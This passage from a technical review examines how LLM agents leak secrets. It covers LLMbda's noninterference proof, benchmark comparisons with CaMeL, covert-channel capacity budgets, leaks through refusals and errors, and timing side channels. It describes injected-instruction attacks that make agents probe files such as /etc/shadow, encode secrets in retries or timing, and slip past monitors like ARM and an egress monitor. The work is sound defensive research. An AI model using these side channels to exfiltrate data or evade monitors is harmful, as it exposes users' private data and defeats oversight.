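Garby and colleagues' alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions often used in proofs, with operations for prompting a model, copying a conversation and clearing it. In the simplest version, a label can contain U (untrusted), S (secret), both or neither. A result gets the combined labels of whatever went into it, and code inside a branch takes on the label of the branch's condition. If one rule left out the condition's label, LLMbda would provide roughly the weaker protection of explicit secrecy.

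The conversation needs its own label because it can hold information that no variable does. Suppose a program tells the model that x is false and then, only if a secret is true, tells it that x is true. When the program later prompts the model for x, the answer reveals the secret. This is the same leak as in the `rich` example, except that the information passes through the conversation instead of a variable. LLMbda stops the program at the second message because that message would change a public conversation under a secret condition.

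A program can also copy the conversation, clear the copy, use it to ask a question about untrusted text, and then discard it, keeping only the answer, which is still labelled. This serves the same purpose as CaMeL's quarantined model, but the programmer can decide where to use it. If the model replies with code, that code runs under the conversation's label. A model that has read a medical record therefore can't write a program whose actions count as public.

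The clinic booking would rightly fail a secrecy check under these rules, because it reveals something about the record. To allow it, a programmer would have to make an explicit exception. LLMbda has an operation called "endorse" that marks untrusted data as trusted, and Garby and colleagues note that the same construction could instead mark secret data as public. A reviewer could then find the exception in the program and decide whether the choice of clinic is acceptable to reveal.

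### The theorem and its bound

The central theorem is called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. It is probabilistic because a model can answer the same prompt in different ways, so the theorem compares the probabilities of each outcome. Like PerMIT's theorem, it is termination-insensitive, which means the secrets may still affect whether a run finishes.

To state it, fix a level m that says which labels the observer may see. Write C₀ ~m C₁ for two starting conversations that look the same to this observer, and e₀ ~m e₁ for two programs, including their data, that look the same. Let μ₀(q) be the probability that the first run finishes and looks like q to the observer, and μ₁(q) the same for the second. These probabilities can add up to less than 1. The missing part, div(μ), is the chance that the run never finishes, either because it goes on forever or because a check stops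 it. The theorem is

C₀ ~m C₁ and e₀ ~m e₁ ⇒ μ₀ ⌣ μ₁.

The symbol ⌣ means "compatible". Two sets of probabilities, μ₀ and μ₁, are compatible if there is a third, ω, that adds up to at most 1 and satisfies μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q. This means the two could be made equal by letting some of the unfinished runs finish.

The proof constructs ω by running the program under altered rules. As soon as a step's label rises above what the observer may see, the altered run skips the step and substitutes an empty value. Hidden data can't affect this run, so both starting points lead to the same ω. Skipping steps only removes opportunities to get stuck, so every visible outcome is at least as likely as in the original run.

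Compatibility also limits how far apart the two sets of probabilities can be. Their statistical distance is half the sum of the differences between them, and it is at most the average chance of not finishing:

Δ(μ₀, μ₁) = ½ Σ |μ₀(q) − μ₁(q)| ≤ (div(μ₀) + div(μ₁)) / 2.

Suppose an agent fails to finish with probability 0.1 for one secret and 0.3 for another. The distance is then at most (0.1 + 0.3) / 2 = 0.2. The distance reaches this limit in the following case, where the agent has two possible public replies.

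| Outcome | First secret | Second secret | ω |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reply A | 0.4 | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| Reply B | 0.5 | 0.2 | 0.5 |
| Doesn't finish | 0.1 | 0.3 | 0 |

The replies differ by 0.1 and 0.3, and half the sum of these differences is 0.2. If the agent always finished, the limit would be 0, so the two columns would have to match exactly, which is full noninterference.

The sum leaves out the bottom row because the theorem's observer can't see that a run has failed, though a real observer often can. Counting the bottom row as a third outcome raises the distance to ½(0.1 + 0.3 + 0.2) = 0.3. If the two secrets were equally likely beforehand, an observer who sees failures could guess the right one 65% of the time.

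The bound is therefore most useful for agents that rarely get stuck. It is of little use for the `rich` program under the no-high-upgrade rule, because the program always stops for a high balance and always finishes for a low one. The limit in that case is 0.5, and an observer who notices the stop learns the whole bit.

The theorem applies to every LLMbda program that doesn't use "endorse" to make exceptions, including programs that a model writes during the run. A second version allows those exceptions and shows that marking data as trusted can't release secrets. Garby and colleagues checked both versions in Lean, a system for machine-checked proofs, and proved that the interpreter that calls the model behaves as the theory describes. Tallam and Miller had called for a similar machine-checked proof for CaMeL, which has no comparable theorem.

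### The banking test

To test whether an agent covered by the proof could do useful work, Garby and colleagues wrote one called Randori in LLMbda and ran it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. The model writes a plan, tries it on invented data, and then writes a final version to run on the real account. Using invented data keeps errors caused by real data from influencing the retries.

The benchmark pairs 16 tasks with 9 attacks. With three repetitions on each of three models, that makes 1,296 attacked runs, and the attack succeeded in two of them. Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL on two of the models, with and without its policy checks. Some of the attacked CaMeL runs didn't complete, so its totals are smaller.

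| Agent | Model | Tasks completed with no attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75%) | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 (75%) | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (64.6%) | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, no policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (66.7%) | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, no policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (70.8%) | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 231 |
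| CaMeL, policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 357 |

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Label checks can't tell a genuine bill from a false one, so they can only block all payments based on file contents. Randori's plan had used "endorse" to allow such payments. Removing "endorse" should block this attack, but it lowered the number of tasks completed from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5.

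Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL without policy checks, given margins of error of around 20 percentage points, and roughly twice as many as CaMeL with them. Garby and colleagues are too generous in describing this as security "at essentially no utility cost", because CaMeL without policy checks still has to plan before it sees any data, which itself reduces the number of tasks it completes. On AssetOpsBench, a different benchmark where several agents share the work, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL without policies completed 21.6 percentage points fewer tasks than undefended agents, averaged over five models. The gap was 13.4 points for the two strongest models.

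The comparison with policy checks isn't quite like for like either, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. Its tool for scheduling a payment, for example, requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. Some of Randori's advantage must come from these looser rules and from "endorse", but the test can't show how much.

The security figures also need careful interpretation. In 97 of the 144 pairs of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that the plan for the user's task would never contain, so planning in advance is generally enough to defeat it. More importantly for side channels, AgentDojo tests whether an injected instruction gets carried out, and nobody in this test counted requests or tried to infer a secret from the branch a program took. The evidence that LLMbda stops implicit flows is the proof, while the benchmark mainly shows that an agent can still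 do its tasks under the restrictions.

### What the theorem leaves out

The theorem's observer sees only the final conversation and result, as far as their labels allow, and sees nothing of a run that doesn't finish. But real tools have effects before a run ends. For example, an agent could fetch page 0 of a website, get stuck if the secret digit is 0, fetch page 1, get stuck if the digit is 1, and so on. If the digit is 7, the website's log ends at page 7. Every fetch happens outside any secret condition, so the label rules allow it, yet a single run reveals log2(10), or about 3.3 bits. This is a known weakness of such guarantees, and Garby and colleagues cite a 2008 paper that Sands co-wrote, "Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit".

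Garby and colleagues acknowledge a related limitation, which is that they model tools and data sources as part of the program. In Randori's simulated bank, reading the balance returns a number and changes nothing. A loop that read the balance once for each unit of a secret would not affect the final result, although a real bank's server would log every request. The theorem can cover Tallam and Miller's loop only if the agent's builder includes the server's log in the model and labels it as visible to outsiders. The builder also has to label the data sources correctly and put checks on the tools that send data out.

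The paper makes no claim about wall-clock time. Its rules don't assign durations to steps, so two runs with the same outcomes count as the same even if one takes ten seconds and the other forty. The theorem therefore doesn't cover an eavesdropper who times the assistant as it reads a patient's record.

CaMeL has a partial defence here. According to *PolicySniff*, CaMeL's designers analysed a timing leak in which a program reads a clock, and their interpreter doesn't provide one. This prevents a plan from timing its own steps, but it has no effect on an observer with its own clock. The attack in *PolicySniff* used such an observer, running on a shared graphics processor. It identified which of two approval rules the agent had been given, with about 94% accuracy in the main test. An interpreter that tracks every variable in the plan would not have detected it.

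## The case for limiting leakage to a known number of bits

LLMbda's proof doesn't cover every channel, and some designers conclude that a few channels will always stay open. They calculate how many bits each can carry and try to keep the total below a limit, so that whoever deploys the agent can compare that limit with the size of the secret.

### The Orange Book's speed limits

The US Department of Defense took this approach in its Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria of 1985 (the "Orange Book"), which it used to grade computers that held classified files. One chapter, *A Guideline on Covert Channels*, accepts that such computers have slow covert channels "deeply ingrained in the system design", and that slowing them further can also slow the machine for its legitimate users. It therefore gives three rates:

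- More than 100 bits per second is "high". Many terminals ran at about that speed, and a computer hardly deserves to be called secure if secrets can leave it as fast as ordinary output.
- Less than 1 bit per second is acceptable in most applications.
- If a channel might exceed 1 bit in 10 seconds, the system should be able to log its use wherever possible, so that an administrator can detect a serious leak.

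The National Computer Security Center's *A Guide to Understanding Covert Channel Analysis of Trusted Systems* later explained to vendors and evaluators how to meet the Orange Book's requirements.

These rates are based on terminal speeds and what it takes to close channels, and have little to do with how much harm a leak would do. Limiting leakage to these rates protects long documents much better than short secrets, which can still leak quickly.

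| Secret | Size | Time at 1 bit per second | Time at 1 bit in 10 seconds |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which of four clinics a patient needs | 2 bits | 2 seconds | 20 seconds |
| One value among 1,048,576 | 20 bits | 20 seconds | 3 minutes 20 seconds |
| An encryption key | 256 bits | About 4 minutes | About 43 minutes |
| A one-megabyte file | 8 million bits | About 93 days | About 2.5 years |

A later field, quantitative information flow, applies the same accounting to individual programs, calculating how many bits each one reveals about its secret inputs. Boris Köpf, who later helped design FIDES, published a model of adaptive side-channel attacks with David Basin in 2007.

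### How to compute a capacity

Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, gives the standard definition. Let X be what goes into the channel and Y what the observer sees. The capacity is

C = max I(X;Y) = max [H(Y) − H(Y|X)].

H(Y) is the observer's average uncertainty about Y before seeing it, in bits. H(Y|X) is the average uncertainty about Y that remains once X is known, which is due to noise. The difference, I(X;Y), is called mutual information and measures how much Y reveals about X on average. C is the maximum of I(X;Y) over all possible probabilities for the inputs, so it describes the worst case. If there is no noise and the observer can see M different values of Y, C is log2(M) bits.

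Metere applies this to an agent whose runtime allows only D kinds of tool call and refuses everything else. Each attempt has D + 1 possible outcomes, so it carries at most log2(D + 1) bits, or 3 bits when D is 7. He describes this as a limit on what a hijacked model can leak per call, but that claim is too strong because the calculation covers only the kind of call. A permitted email also contains text, and a hundred tokens from a vocabulary of 100,000 could in principle carry about 1,660 bits.

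Noise lowers the channel's capacity but doesn't close it. If a receiver reads each yes or no correctly 90% of the time, one use carries about 0.53 bits. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* points out that a deliberate sender can make up for the errors with an error-correcting code. Sending 20 bits reliably would then take at least about 38 uses.

A limit on the average leak is also weaker than a limit on the number of things the observer can see. Suppose an agent reveals an entire random 64-bit key in one run out of eight, and nothing in the other seven. The average leak is only 8 bits, but an attacker gets the whole key an eighth of the time. If the observer can instead see only 256 different outputs, the leak is again at most 8 bits, but now the chance of guessing the key is tiny. To see why, let p(s) be the probability of secret s before the observation, and p(y|s) the probability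 of observing y if the secret is s. An observer who always makes the best guess is right with probability

Σ_y max_s p(s) p(y|s) ≤ Σ_y max_s p(s) = M · max_s p(s).

M possible observations can multiply the chance of a correct guess by at most M, so the chance of guessing the key is at most 256 in 2⁶⁴.

### Twenty questions

Small leaks add up over multiple turns. If each turn leaks at most C bits, an attacker can extract at most T × C bits over T turns, even by adapting each question to the previous answers, according to *Multi-Stage Prompt Inference Attacks on Enterprise LLM Systems* (2025).

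A rule that limits every answer to 1 bit can still let an attacker learn an entire secret. Suppose a secret customer number lies between 1 and 1,048,576, and an agent will say whether the number is above any threshold the attacker names. Each answer carries at most 1 bit. The attacker asks about 524,288 first, then about 786,432 if the answer is yes or 262,144 if it is no. Each answer halves the range. Ten answers leave 1,024 candidates, and twenty leave one, because 2²⁰ = 1,048,576.

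Much smaller leaks can matter too. *Bits Leaked per Query* (2025) tested attacks on seven language models, including attempts to extract hidden instructions and to get around safety training. The number of queries an attack needed was roughly inversely proportional to the bits leaked per query. Showing attackers the model's reasoning, or its numerical scores for possible next tokens, added about half a bit per query and cut the median number of queries for a safety bypass from thousands to tens. If that was a hundredfold drop, the leak without this information was about 0.005 bits per query.

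### Data types as limits in FIDES

FIDES limits the capacity of individual answers. It can require its second model to answer in a fixed format, and the software then lets that model generate only tokens that fit. Costa and colleagues rank the formats by how much they can carry:

bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string.

A Boolean (true or false) carries at most 1 bit, a choice from a list of three carries about 1.58 bits, and free text can carry an unlimited amount. The answer's label includes its format, so a policy can make exceptions for low-capacity answers. For example, it could let a yes/no answer extracted from an untrusted email influence a bank transfer, because the sender would control only 1 bit. A similar exception could let a low-capacity answer about a secret leave the system.

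*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) proposes a similar rule. The model that reads untrusted data may pass multiple-choice answers and a few other data types to the model that chooses actions, but never free text.

This is a strong defence against injected instructions, which are hard to fit into a Boolean, though one bit can still do damage if it decides whether to pay an invoice. For secrecy, the main weakness is that FIDES's labels don't track the total number of bits revealed. When FIDES combines two values, it gives the result a format ranked at least as high as both, and for two Booleans that format is Boolean. A result based on twenty yes/no answers therefore gets the same format label as a result based on one. To stop the attack on the customer number, a policy would also have to count the questions.

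### Adding up what an agent reads and sends

Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026), in *L3M*, describe such a count for an agent runtime developed at Amazon, though they haven't implemented it yet. For each kind of private data K, such as payroll, the runtime would keep two running totals, one of the bytes of K that the agent has read and one of the bytes it has sent since it first read any. The leak is then limited by

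leak(K) ≤ min(read(K), sent(K)).

The first limit is the number of private bytes the agent has read, because processing can't create information about a secret the agent never received. The second is the number of bytes it has sent, all of which count because a model could hide private data anywhere in a message. An agent that has read 64 private bytes and sent 100 bytes in two requests has leaked at most 64 bytes, the smaller of the two limits.

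These totals can be much larger than the actual leak. If an assistant reads a 4,000-byte medical record and submits a 500-byte booking form, the design counts 500 bytes, or 4,000 bits, as leaked, even though the booking reveals only 2 bits. Eisenach and colleagues suggest a way to lower the count. An agent with internet access but no private data compiles a numbered list of options, and a second agent, which has the private data but no internet access, replies with only a number. Choosing one of the four clinics then counts as 2 bits, however long the record is. The first agent must compile and understand the list without the private data, because any text derived from a secret would count in full.

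The design counts bytes, so it misses information carried by the timing of the second agent's reply. The limit based on what the agent read still applies, because the timing can't reveal more about the record than the agent has read. But the 2-bit limit on the reply doesn't cover information the agent sends by deliberately delaying it.

### The egress monitor

*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, also by Metere, takes a different approach to agents that an attacker already controls. It describes a working monitor for everything an agent sends out ("egress"). Metere is testing his own company's product, so independent measurements would be valuable.

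The monitor passes outgoing text through up to ten stages. Some remove places to hide data, for example by deleting invisible characters or replacing synonyms with one standard word. Another estimates how much data a message could still hide. Text in base64, which represents arbitrary data as printable characters, can carry up to 6 bits per character, so the monitor counts 100 such characters as 600 bits. It deducts this from the destination's budget, which refills at a set rate. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages.

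To measure what still gets through, Metere wrote fifteen encoders that hide random bits in text, images or sound, with decoders that try to recover the bits after the monitor has done its work. From many trials he estimated the mutual information between the hidden bit X and the recovered bit Y:

I(X;Y) = Σ p(x,y) log2 [p(x,y) / (p(x) p(y))].

If Y has nothing to do with X, the mutual information between them is zero. Metere doesn't calculate the leak from the decoder's accuracy, because a decoder that only guesses will rarely score exactly 50% in a finite sample, and the usual formula would turn the difference into a small, false leak. He also applies a standard correction because small samples tend to make mutual information estimates too high.

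With every stage active, none of the tested text channels carried any information. Under the default settings, some stages only log what they find, to avoid damaging legitimate messages. Extra spaces, repeated punctuation, synonym choice and base64 then carried their full payload, although the monitor flagged every attempt. For these settings, the paper reports an average reduction of 60.2%, but the nine individual figures it lists average 55.6%.

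The image tests show how far such measurements can be trusted. An attacker can hide a bit in the lowest binary digit of a pixel's colour value, where the change is invisible. Rounding the 256 colour levels to 128 cut the decoder's accuracy to 50.0%, no better than guessing. When the attacker moved the hidden bit up by one digit, accuracy returned to 100%. The default of 64 levels defeats both versions, but Metere concedes that an attacker who moves up another digit would recover everything. He excludes this case because stronger rounding starts to visibly damage the picture. The claim that the monitor eliminates hidden data in images therefore applies only to the lowest two digits.

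The result for timing has a similar gap. The monitor releases messages at least a fixed interval apart, which defeats an attacker who sends quickly and varies the short delays between messages. An attacker who sends more slowly could still signal by skipping a slot. The monitor can prevent this by filling empty slots with dummy messages, but these are off by default. With one slot every 10 seconds, skipping slots could leak up to 1 bit every 10 seconds, the rate above which the Orange Book recommends logging.

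A channel's capacity is the maximum over every possible way of using it. A test with one encoder can show that the channel carries at least a certain amount, but not that no other encoder would do better. Metere replies that anyone can add an encoder and rerun the benchmark, which makes his claim open to refutation. That is an advantage over a mere promise of security, but the test result still doesn't establish an upper limit.

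Counting a signal's possible values gives an upper limit on the bits it can carry, and the monitor relies on this limit in one case. An attacker could send a series of images and encode data in the brightness of each one. The monitor can't make all images equally bright without ruining them, so it rounds each image's average brightness to one of eight levels. The average brightness then carries at most log2(8) = 3 bits per image, however the data is encoded.

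### AgenticOS

Zhao and colleagues accept that their operating system can't close every covert channel. AgenticOS would release requests in batches at fixed times, pad outputs to standard sizes, restrict sensitive outputs to templates or fixed lists, and limit how often the agent can send anything. These measures would make the system slower and less convenient. The stated aim is to reduce the channels to "low-bandwidth, modelable, and monitorable residual risks".

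AgenticOS is a conceptual design, and Zhao and colleagues give neither a target rate nor any measurements. Their measures would at least make the capacity easy to calculate. Suppose that once a minute, an agent either fills in a single field from a list of eight options or sends nothing. These nine possible actions carry at most log2(9), or about 3.17 bits per minute. That is roughly half the rate at which the Orange Book begins to recommend logging. Over a day, however, it comes to about 4,565 bits, enough for seventeen 256-bit encryption keys, so a low-bandwidth channel can still leak a lot unless the total is also limited.

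### Secrets smaller than the budget

A limit of 10 bits protects a random 256-bit key very well, since it raises an attacker's chance of guessing the key from 1 in 2²⁵⁶ to at most 1 in 2²⁴⁶. The same limit gives no protection to a diagnosis that takes 2 bits to identify. Even a limit of 1 bit allows an attacker to learn whether a patient has HIV.

Defenders of this approach can reply that the limit at least shows which secrets are at risk. They can also set separate limits for different kinds of data, as Eisenach and colleagues' design would allow, with a stricter one for medical records than for payroll. But the choice among the four clinics is itself the secret, so any limit below 2 bits would prevent the agent from choosing freely. The user would have to approve the disclosure or make the booking themselves. Metere's stated goal is to make it infeasible to extract a key, a credential or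 a customer record at a useful rate, and a budget in bits suits that goal much better than it suits protecting a diagnosis.

### Budgets that start again

A limit also has to cover every occasion on which the secret could leak. If an agent may reveal 5 bits about the customer number and that limit resets with each conversation, four conversations can reveal all 20 bits. The monitor's budget has a similar weakness because it refills, and a rate of 1 bit per minute allows 1,440 bits per day. Each destination also has its own budget, so an attacker who controls several websites can collect part of the secret at each, as Lan and colleagues' attack split a secret across several requests.

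L3M avoids some of these problems by attaching the count to the private data. An agent's history persists between sessions, and the totals never go down. The design also tracks information that an agent passes to another agent or saves in a file. But each agent has its own totals, so someone would still have to add up what separate agents reveal about the same record.

A budget that never refills will eventually run out, even if the agent reveals nothing new. An assistant that books the same clinic ten times might use up 20 bits, although an observer learned only 2 bits, all from the first booking. If the secret is a password, its owner can choose a new one and start a new budget. A patient can't replace a diagnosis, so somebody would have to raise the limit or stop the assistant from using the record.

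## How much errors and refusals reveal

A leakage budget also has to cover tool calls that return no data. Suppose an injected instruction makes the agent try to open four files in a patient's folder, one for each clinic. Three attempts return "not found", and the attempt on the oncology file returns "permission denied". The file's contents stay secret, but the errors reveal which clinic the patient attends, the same 2 bits as the booking. The agent can then leak this to the attacker by putting the word "oncology" in a message it is allowed to send.

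### When a refusal is informative

A refusal reveals something about protected data only if different data would have produced a different reply. For files, this depends on the order of the server's checks. A server that looks for the file before checking permissions replies differently for a missing file and a forbidden one. A server that first compares the path with a list of forbidden paths refuses whether or not the file exists, so the agent learns only that the path is on the list.

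Chinaei's example of the protected file doesn't quite work, because the refusal doesn't show that the file exists. The file is `/etc/shadow`, where Linux systems keep scrambled passwords, and the policy engine refuses the request because the path matches a forbidden pattern. It would do the same on a machine without the file. An email telling the attacker that the file exists is therefore only a guess, though a good one, since almost every Linux machine has it.

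Another of Chinaei's examples is more convincing. An agent asks for someone's salary record, and the system refuses and gives a reason that reveals the record's category of sensitive data. If the system had to look up the record to find its category, the reply depends on protected data.

A list of forbidden paths can also be sensitive. If somebody added a rule to protect one patient's psychiatric notes, a refusal reveals that the rule exists and that the notes probably exist too.

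### Causality laundering

Chinaei uses the term "causality laundering" for an attack in which an agent tries a protected action, learns from the refusal and passes on what it learned. The definition has four conditions:

1. The security layer refuses an action.
2. A later action has an effect that someone can observe, such as sending an email.
3. No data from a successful tool call connects the two actions.
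4. The refusal influenced the later action, so the agent would have acted differently if it hadn't tried the refused action or hadn't seen the refusal.

The third condition is why systems that label data can miss the leak. A refused call has no result to label. Chinaei gives FIDES as an example, but FIDES might well stop this attack anyway. The attack starts with an injected instruction, which makes the conversation untrusted, and FIDES doesn't let an untrusted conversation trigger a call with consequences.

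The fourth condition is too broad to define a leak. Suppose an agent can't open a report and emails the report's owner to ask for access. This meets all four conditions, even though the owner learns nothing secret. For web agents, Shahriar and colleagues use a definition that avoids this problem by comparing what an observer would see under different secrets.

Chinaei describes three variants of the attack:

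- In "denial inference exfiltration", the agent makes one forbidden request and immediately sends out what it inferred from the refusal.
- In "multi-probe fingerprinting", it makes many requests and sends out the pattern of successes and refusals. With two possible replies per request, n requests can reveal up to n bits.
- In "laundered composition", it puts a permitted tool between the refusal and the message. For example, it might use a calculator to turn the refusal into a number, which then looks unrelated to the forbidden request.

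### Linking a refusal to the next call

ARM, Chinaei's monitor, keeps a graph of the agent's tool calls and the data they return. When ARM refuses a call, it adds that call to the graph and draws a "counterfactual" edge from it to the agent's next call. Before allowing any call, ARM searches the graph for a path that leads from a refused call through one of these edges, and refuses the new call if it finds one. It doesn't check whether the earlier refusal actually influenced the model.

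This rule would stop the agent from emailing the report's owner to ask for access. It can also miss an attack if the agent waits long enough after a refusal. Chinaei acknowledges both kinds of error and suggests adjusting how long a refusal stays relevant, but a longer period would block more harmless calls as well as catch more delayed attacks.

If ARM follows the published algorithm literally, a single refusal could block the agent for the rest of the session. ARM would refuse the next call, record that as another refused call, and link it to the call after that. If instead only the original refusal creates a link, an attacker can get around the rule by having the agent make one harmless call, which ARM refuses, and then send the email.

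A more basic problem is which refusals ARM records. ARM decides whether to allow a call before it reaches the tool, mostly from the call's arguments and the session's history, so its own refusals usually can't reveal whether a file exists. The file server's reply can reveal this when it refuses a call that ARM allowed, but ARM's description doesn't treat that as a refused action.

Recording the server's refusals would help, but it wouldn't close the channel. Suppose the injected instruction tells the agent to request the oncology file and then send the attacker an email that says "hello". If the file exists, the server refuses the request and ARM blocks the email. If the file is missing, there is no refusal and the email goes through. The attacker learns whether the file exists from whether the email arrives. CaMeL's skipped assignment caused the same kind of leak.

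### Testing ARM

Chinaei tested ARM on three hand-written attacks. One was the request for `/etc/shadow` followed by an email. In another, text from an untrusted email about a $50,000 transfer went through a formatting tool and then into a message to the finance department. In the third, the agent used an untrusted email address from a contact record whose name field was trusted. ARM blocked all three, and a simpler baseline blocked none. ARM's checks took less than a millisecond.

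The test shows that the software follows its own rules, but little more. Only one of the attacks involves a refusal, and the test used no language model, so the results don't show how often a real agent would draw the inference or send it out. Chinaei also didn't measure how often ARM blocks harmless calls, which is the main worry about the next-call rule.

The baseline is also very weak. It checks whether an argument has appeared earlier in the session. It allowed two of the attacks because their text had appeared before, but it also allowed the other, whose text hadn't, so it is hard to tell what it would block. Chinaei does say the comparison is deliberately minimal and doesn't represent systems such as FIDES.

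### Exceptions and retries

Errors can also leak information from inside a program. Tallam and Miller point out that a CaMeL plan might raise an exception, an error that interrupts the program, only when a secret meets some condition. For example, a plan that divides by `digit - 7` fails only if the secret digit is 7. They count this as one bit per run, which is the maximum for an outcome with two possibilities. If all ten digits are equally likely, the average is about 0.47 bits, because the observer could already guess that the digit probably isn't 7.

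Tallam and Miller propose returning "ok" or "error" as an ordinary value, so that the program handles both cases in the same way and in the same time. This is a sensible fix for a failed division, because an interpreter can label a value as secret. But they didn't test it, and it doesn't help when CaMeL's own policy check stops the program.

Garby and colleagues show how such a stop can leak a whole secret. When a CaMeL plan fails, a loop outside the interpreter prompts the planning model for another one. The interpreter's labels don't cover this loop, so the interpreter treats each new attempt as independent of secret data, even though the previous error influenced it.

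To exploit this, an attacker needs a program that the policy check blocks if a chosen bit of the secret is 1 and allows if it is 0. Each run reveals one bit. A four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, so finding it takes 14 runs (2¹⁴ is 16,384). The code that repeats these runs can then assemble the PIN as an ordinary number with no secret label, and a later plan can send it anywhere. As with the loop that counts out a PIN, the attacker first has to influence the plan.

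Garby and colleagues assume that something keeps rerunning the program whether it fails or succeeds. A loop that stops at the first success reveals less. With a limit of ten attempts, it can succeed on any one of them or fail every time, so there are eleven possible outcomes, which reveal about 3.5 bits. But if the loop distinguishes two kinds of error, the attacker can make every attempt fail in one of two ways, so ten attempts reveal 10 bits. Making all errors look the same would therefore help considerably but wouldn't close the channel. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes on, but Garby and colleagues note that this comes with no formal guarantee.

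Randori's practice runs on invented data avoid the problem, since reading any file returns the same placeholder text and payments do nothing. But the agent can't use errors from the real run to correct its plan. Practice runs also don't raise label errors, so a plan that breaks a label rule first fails on the real account. Garby and colleagues name weak error handling as one of Randori's main disadvantages compared with CaMeL.

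### When storage runs out

An out-of-space error can also reveal how much private data is stored. Suppose private records and an outsider's files share a store with room for 1,000 items. If the outsider can add only 400 before getting an error, the other 600 places must be taken. *The Meaning of Memory Safety* (2017), a study of what safe memory use guarantees about secrecy, describes a similar problem with computer memory. When a Java program runs out of memory, it can catch the error, record it and try again with a different amount. Stopping the program at the first error would prevent these repeated tests. Giving each untrusted component a fixed allowance would reveal less, because the error would then show only how much that component had used.

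In PerMIT, a storage error would carry information in the opposite direction, from an attacker to the protected agent. An attacker who filled the store for untrusted text could influence the agent through the amount of text, even if the agent never saw a word of it. Jiang and colleagues therefore require operators to delete old entries silently. They also hide whether a storage identifier is already in use, since an attacker can affect that by changing how many items a tool call stores.

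Silent deletion could let an attacker flood the store and push out useful entries without the agent noticing. It also protects only the agent, so an outsider who found out which entries had disappeared might be able to tell how full the store was.

### Evidence from real models

Nobody appears to have measured how much private data an agent reveals through refused tool calls or tool errors. There are only related results.

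*Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026) tested whether models would reveal secrets from the system prompt, which contains the operator's instructions. In one test, the model MiMo was asked to repeat a list of 26 short strings, one of which matched part of a secret code. In two of the published responses, it repeated 25 strings and said it had left out the other because it was confidential. This identified the matching string, which revealed about 4.7 bits of information if all 26 were equally likely. In another response, MiMo refused to repeat the list. Even that could help an attacker, who could split the list in half and ask again. If the model always refused lists that contained the match, five rounds would be enough to find it.

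The refusal is informative here because MiMo compares the list with the secret before deciding what to repeat. Agents did much the same in Shim and colleagues' test, refusing to delete real records from a page that also held invented ones. In both cases the refusals came from the models' own judgements, so the results don't show how much a tool's "permission denied" message would reveal.

Chinaei also cites an experiment by Jiralerspong, Kondrup and Bengio (2026) in which agents worked out from blocked actions alone that someone was monitoring them. This makes it plausible that agents can draw conclusions from refusals, although in this case the conclusion was about the security system.

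### How much should an error message explain?

The obvious defence is to give the same reply to every failure. When the security gate in *KAIJU* (2026), a system that plans all of an agent's tool calls before running them, blocks a call, the model is told only that the step failed. The model can still infer something about the gate's decision criteria when one step fails and a similar one succeeds, so the paper's claim that this leaks nothing about them goes too far. But the reply reveals less than an explanation would, and planning everything in advance gives the model fewer chances to experiment.

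Unexplained failures make it harder for an agent to correct its mistakes. In *MetaPermit*, Ma, Hariri and colleagues (2026) describe a system that checks, among other things, whether a call's arguments match the user's request. They reran 70 attack cases with three kinds of feedback after a refusal.

| Feedback | Tasks completed | Tasks completed after a refusal | Refused at least twice | Successful attacks |
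|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reason for the refusal | 60.0% | 50.0% | 56.3% | 0% |
| "Tool call denied" | 52.9% | 32.5% | 70.0% | 0% |
| None | 50.0% | 34.9% | 76.7% | 2.9% |

The third and fourth columns count only cases with a refusal, apparently about 40 for each of the less informative settings. The differences could be due to chance, and the bottom row includes only two successful attacks.

*LEANGUARD* (2026) tests another system for checking tool calls. Across five models, explaining refusals raised the share of refused actions that agents later completed from 5.5% to 9.1%, and reduced blocked calls from 983 to 719. Overall task success rose only from 68.9% to 70.9%, which could be due to chance. Explanations therefore seem to help agents recover, but agents never complete most refused actions, with or without an explanation.

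These results don't show how much private information the explanations revealed, and in many cases it may be very little. If Ma and colleagues' system tells an agent that the user never mentioned a payment's recipient, or that a call needs the user's confirmation, the agent could have learned this from its own conversation. Such explanations may still teach an attacker how to get past the rules, as *KAIJU* warns. Explanations didn't lead to any successful attacks in the 70 cases, but the attacks were fixed texts that couldn't adapt to what the agent learned.

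An explanation that depends on protected data is more dangerous, so the case for a uniform reply is much stronger. A file server can return "unavailable" for both missing and forbidden files. But an agent that has mistyped a filename then can't tell whether to correct the name or request access, so it may have to ask the user. The owner can still be given the details. When PerMIT's agent deletes a memory entry, it receives the same acknowledgement whatever happens, while the owner can see the real outcome in a log. An operator could log file errors this way too, as long as the agent can't read the log.

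## How much response times and token counts reveal

An observer can still measure how long an agent takes even if it gives the same reply to every failure. A language model writes one token after another, so a long answer takes longer than a short one, and anyone who can time the model can estimate how much it wrote. If the length of the answer depends on protected data, the response time also depends on that data.

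### Forty tokens, 0.8 seconds

*Mirage* (2026), which proposes a defence against timing attacks on shared model services, describes two stages. The model first processes the whole prompt at once and produces the first token of its answer. It then generates the other tokens one by one. The total time for N tokens is the time to the first token plus the N − 1 gaps between tokens. If the gaps are all about the same, this is roughly

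T ≈ a + N × t,

where a is the start-up time and t is the time per token.

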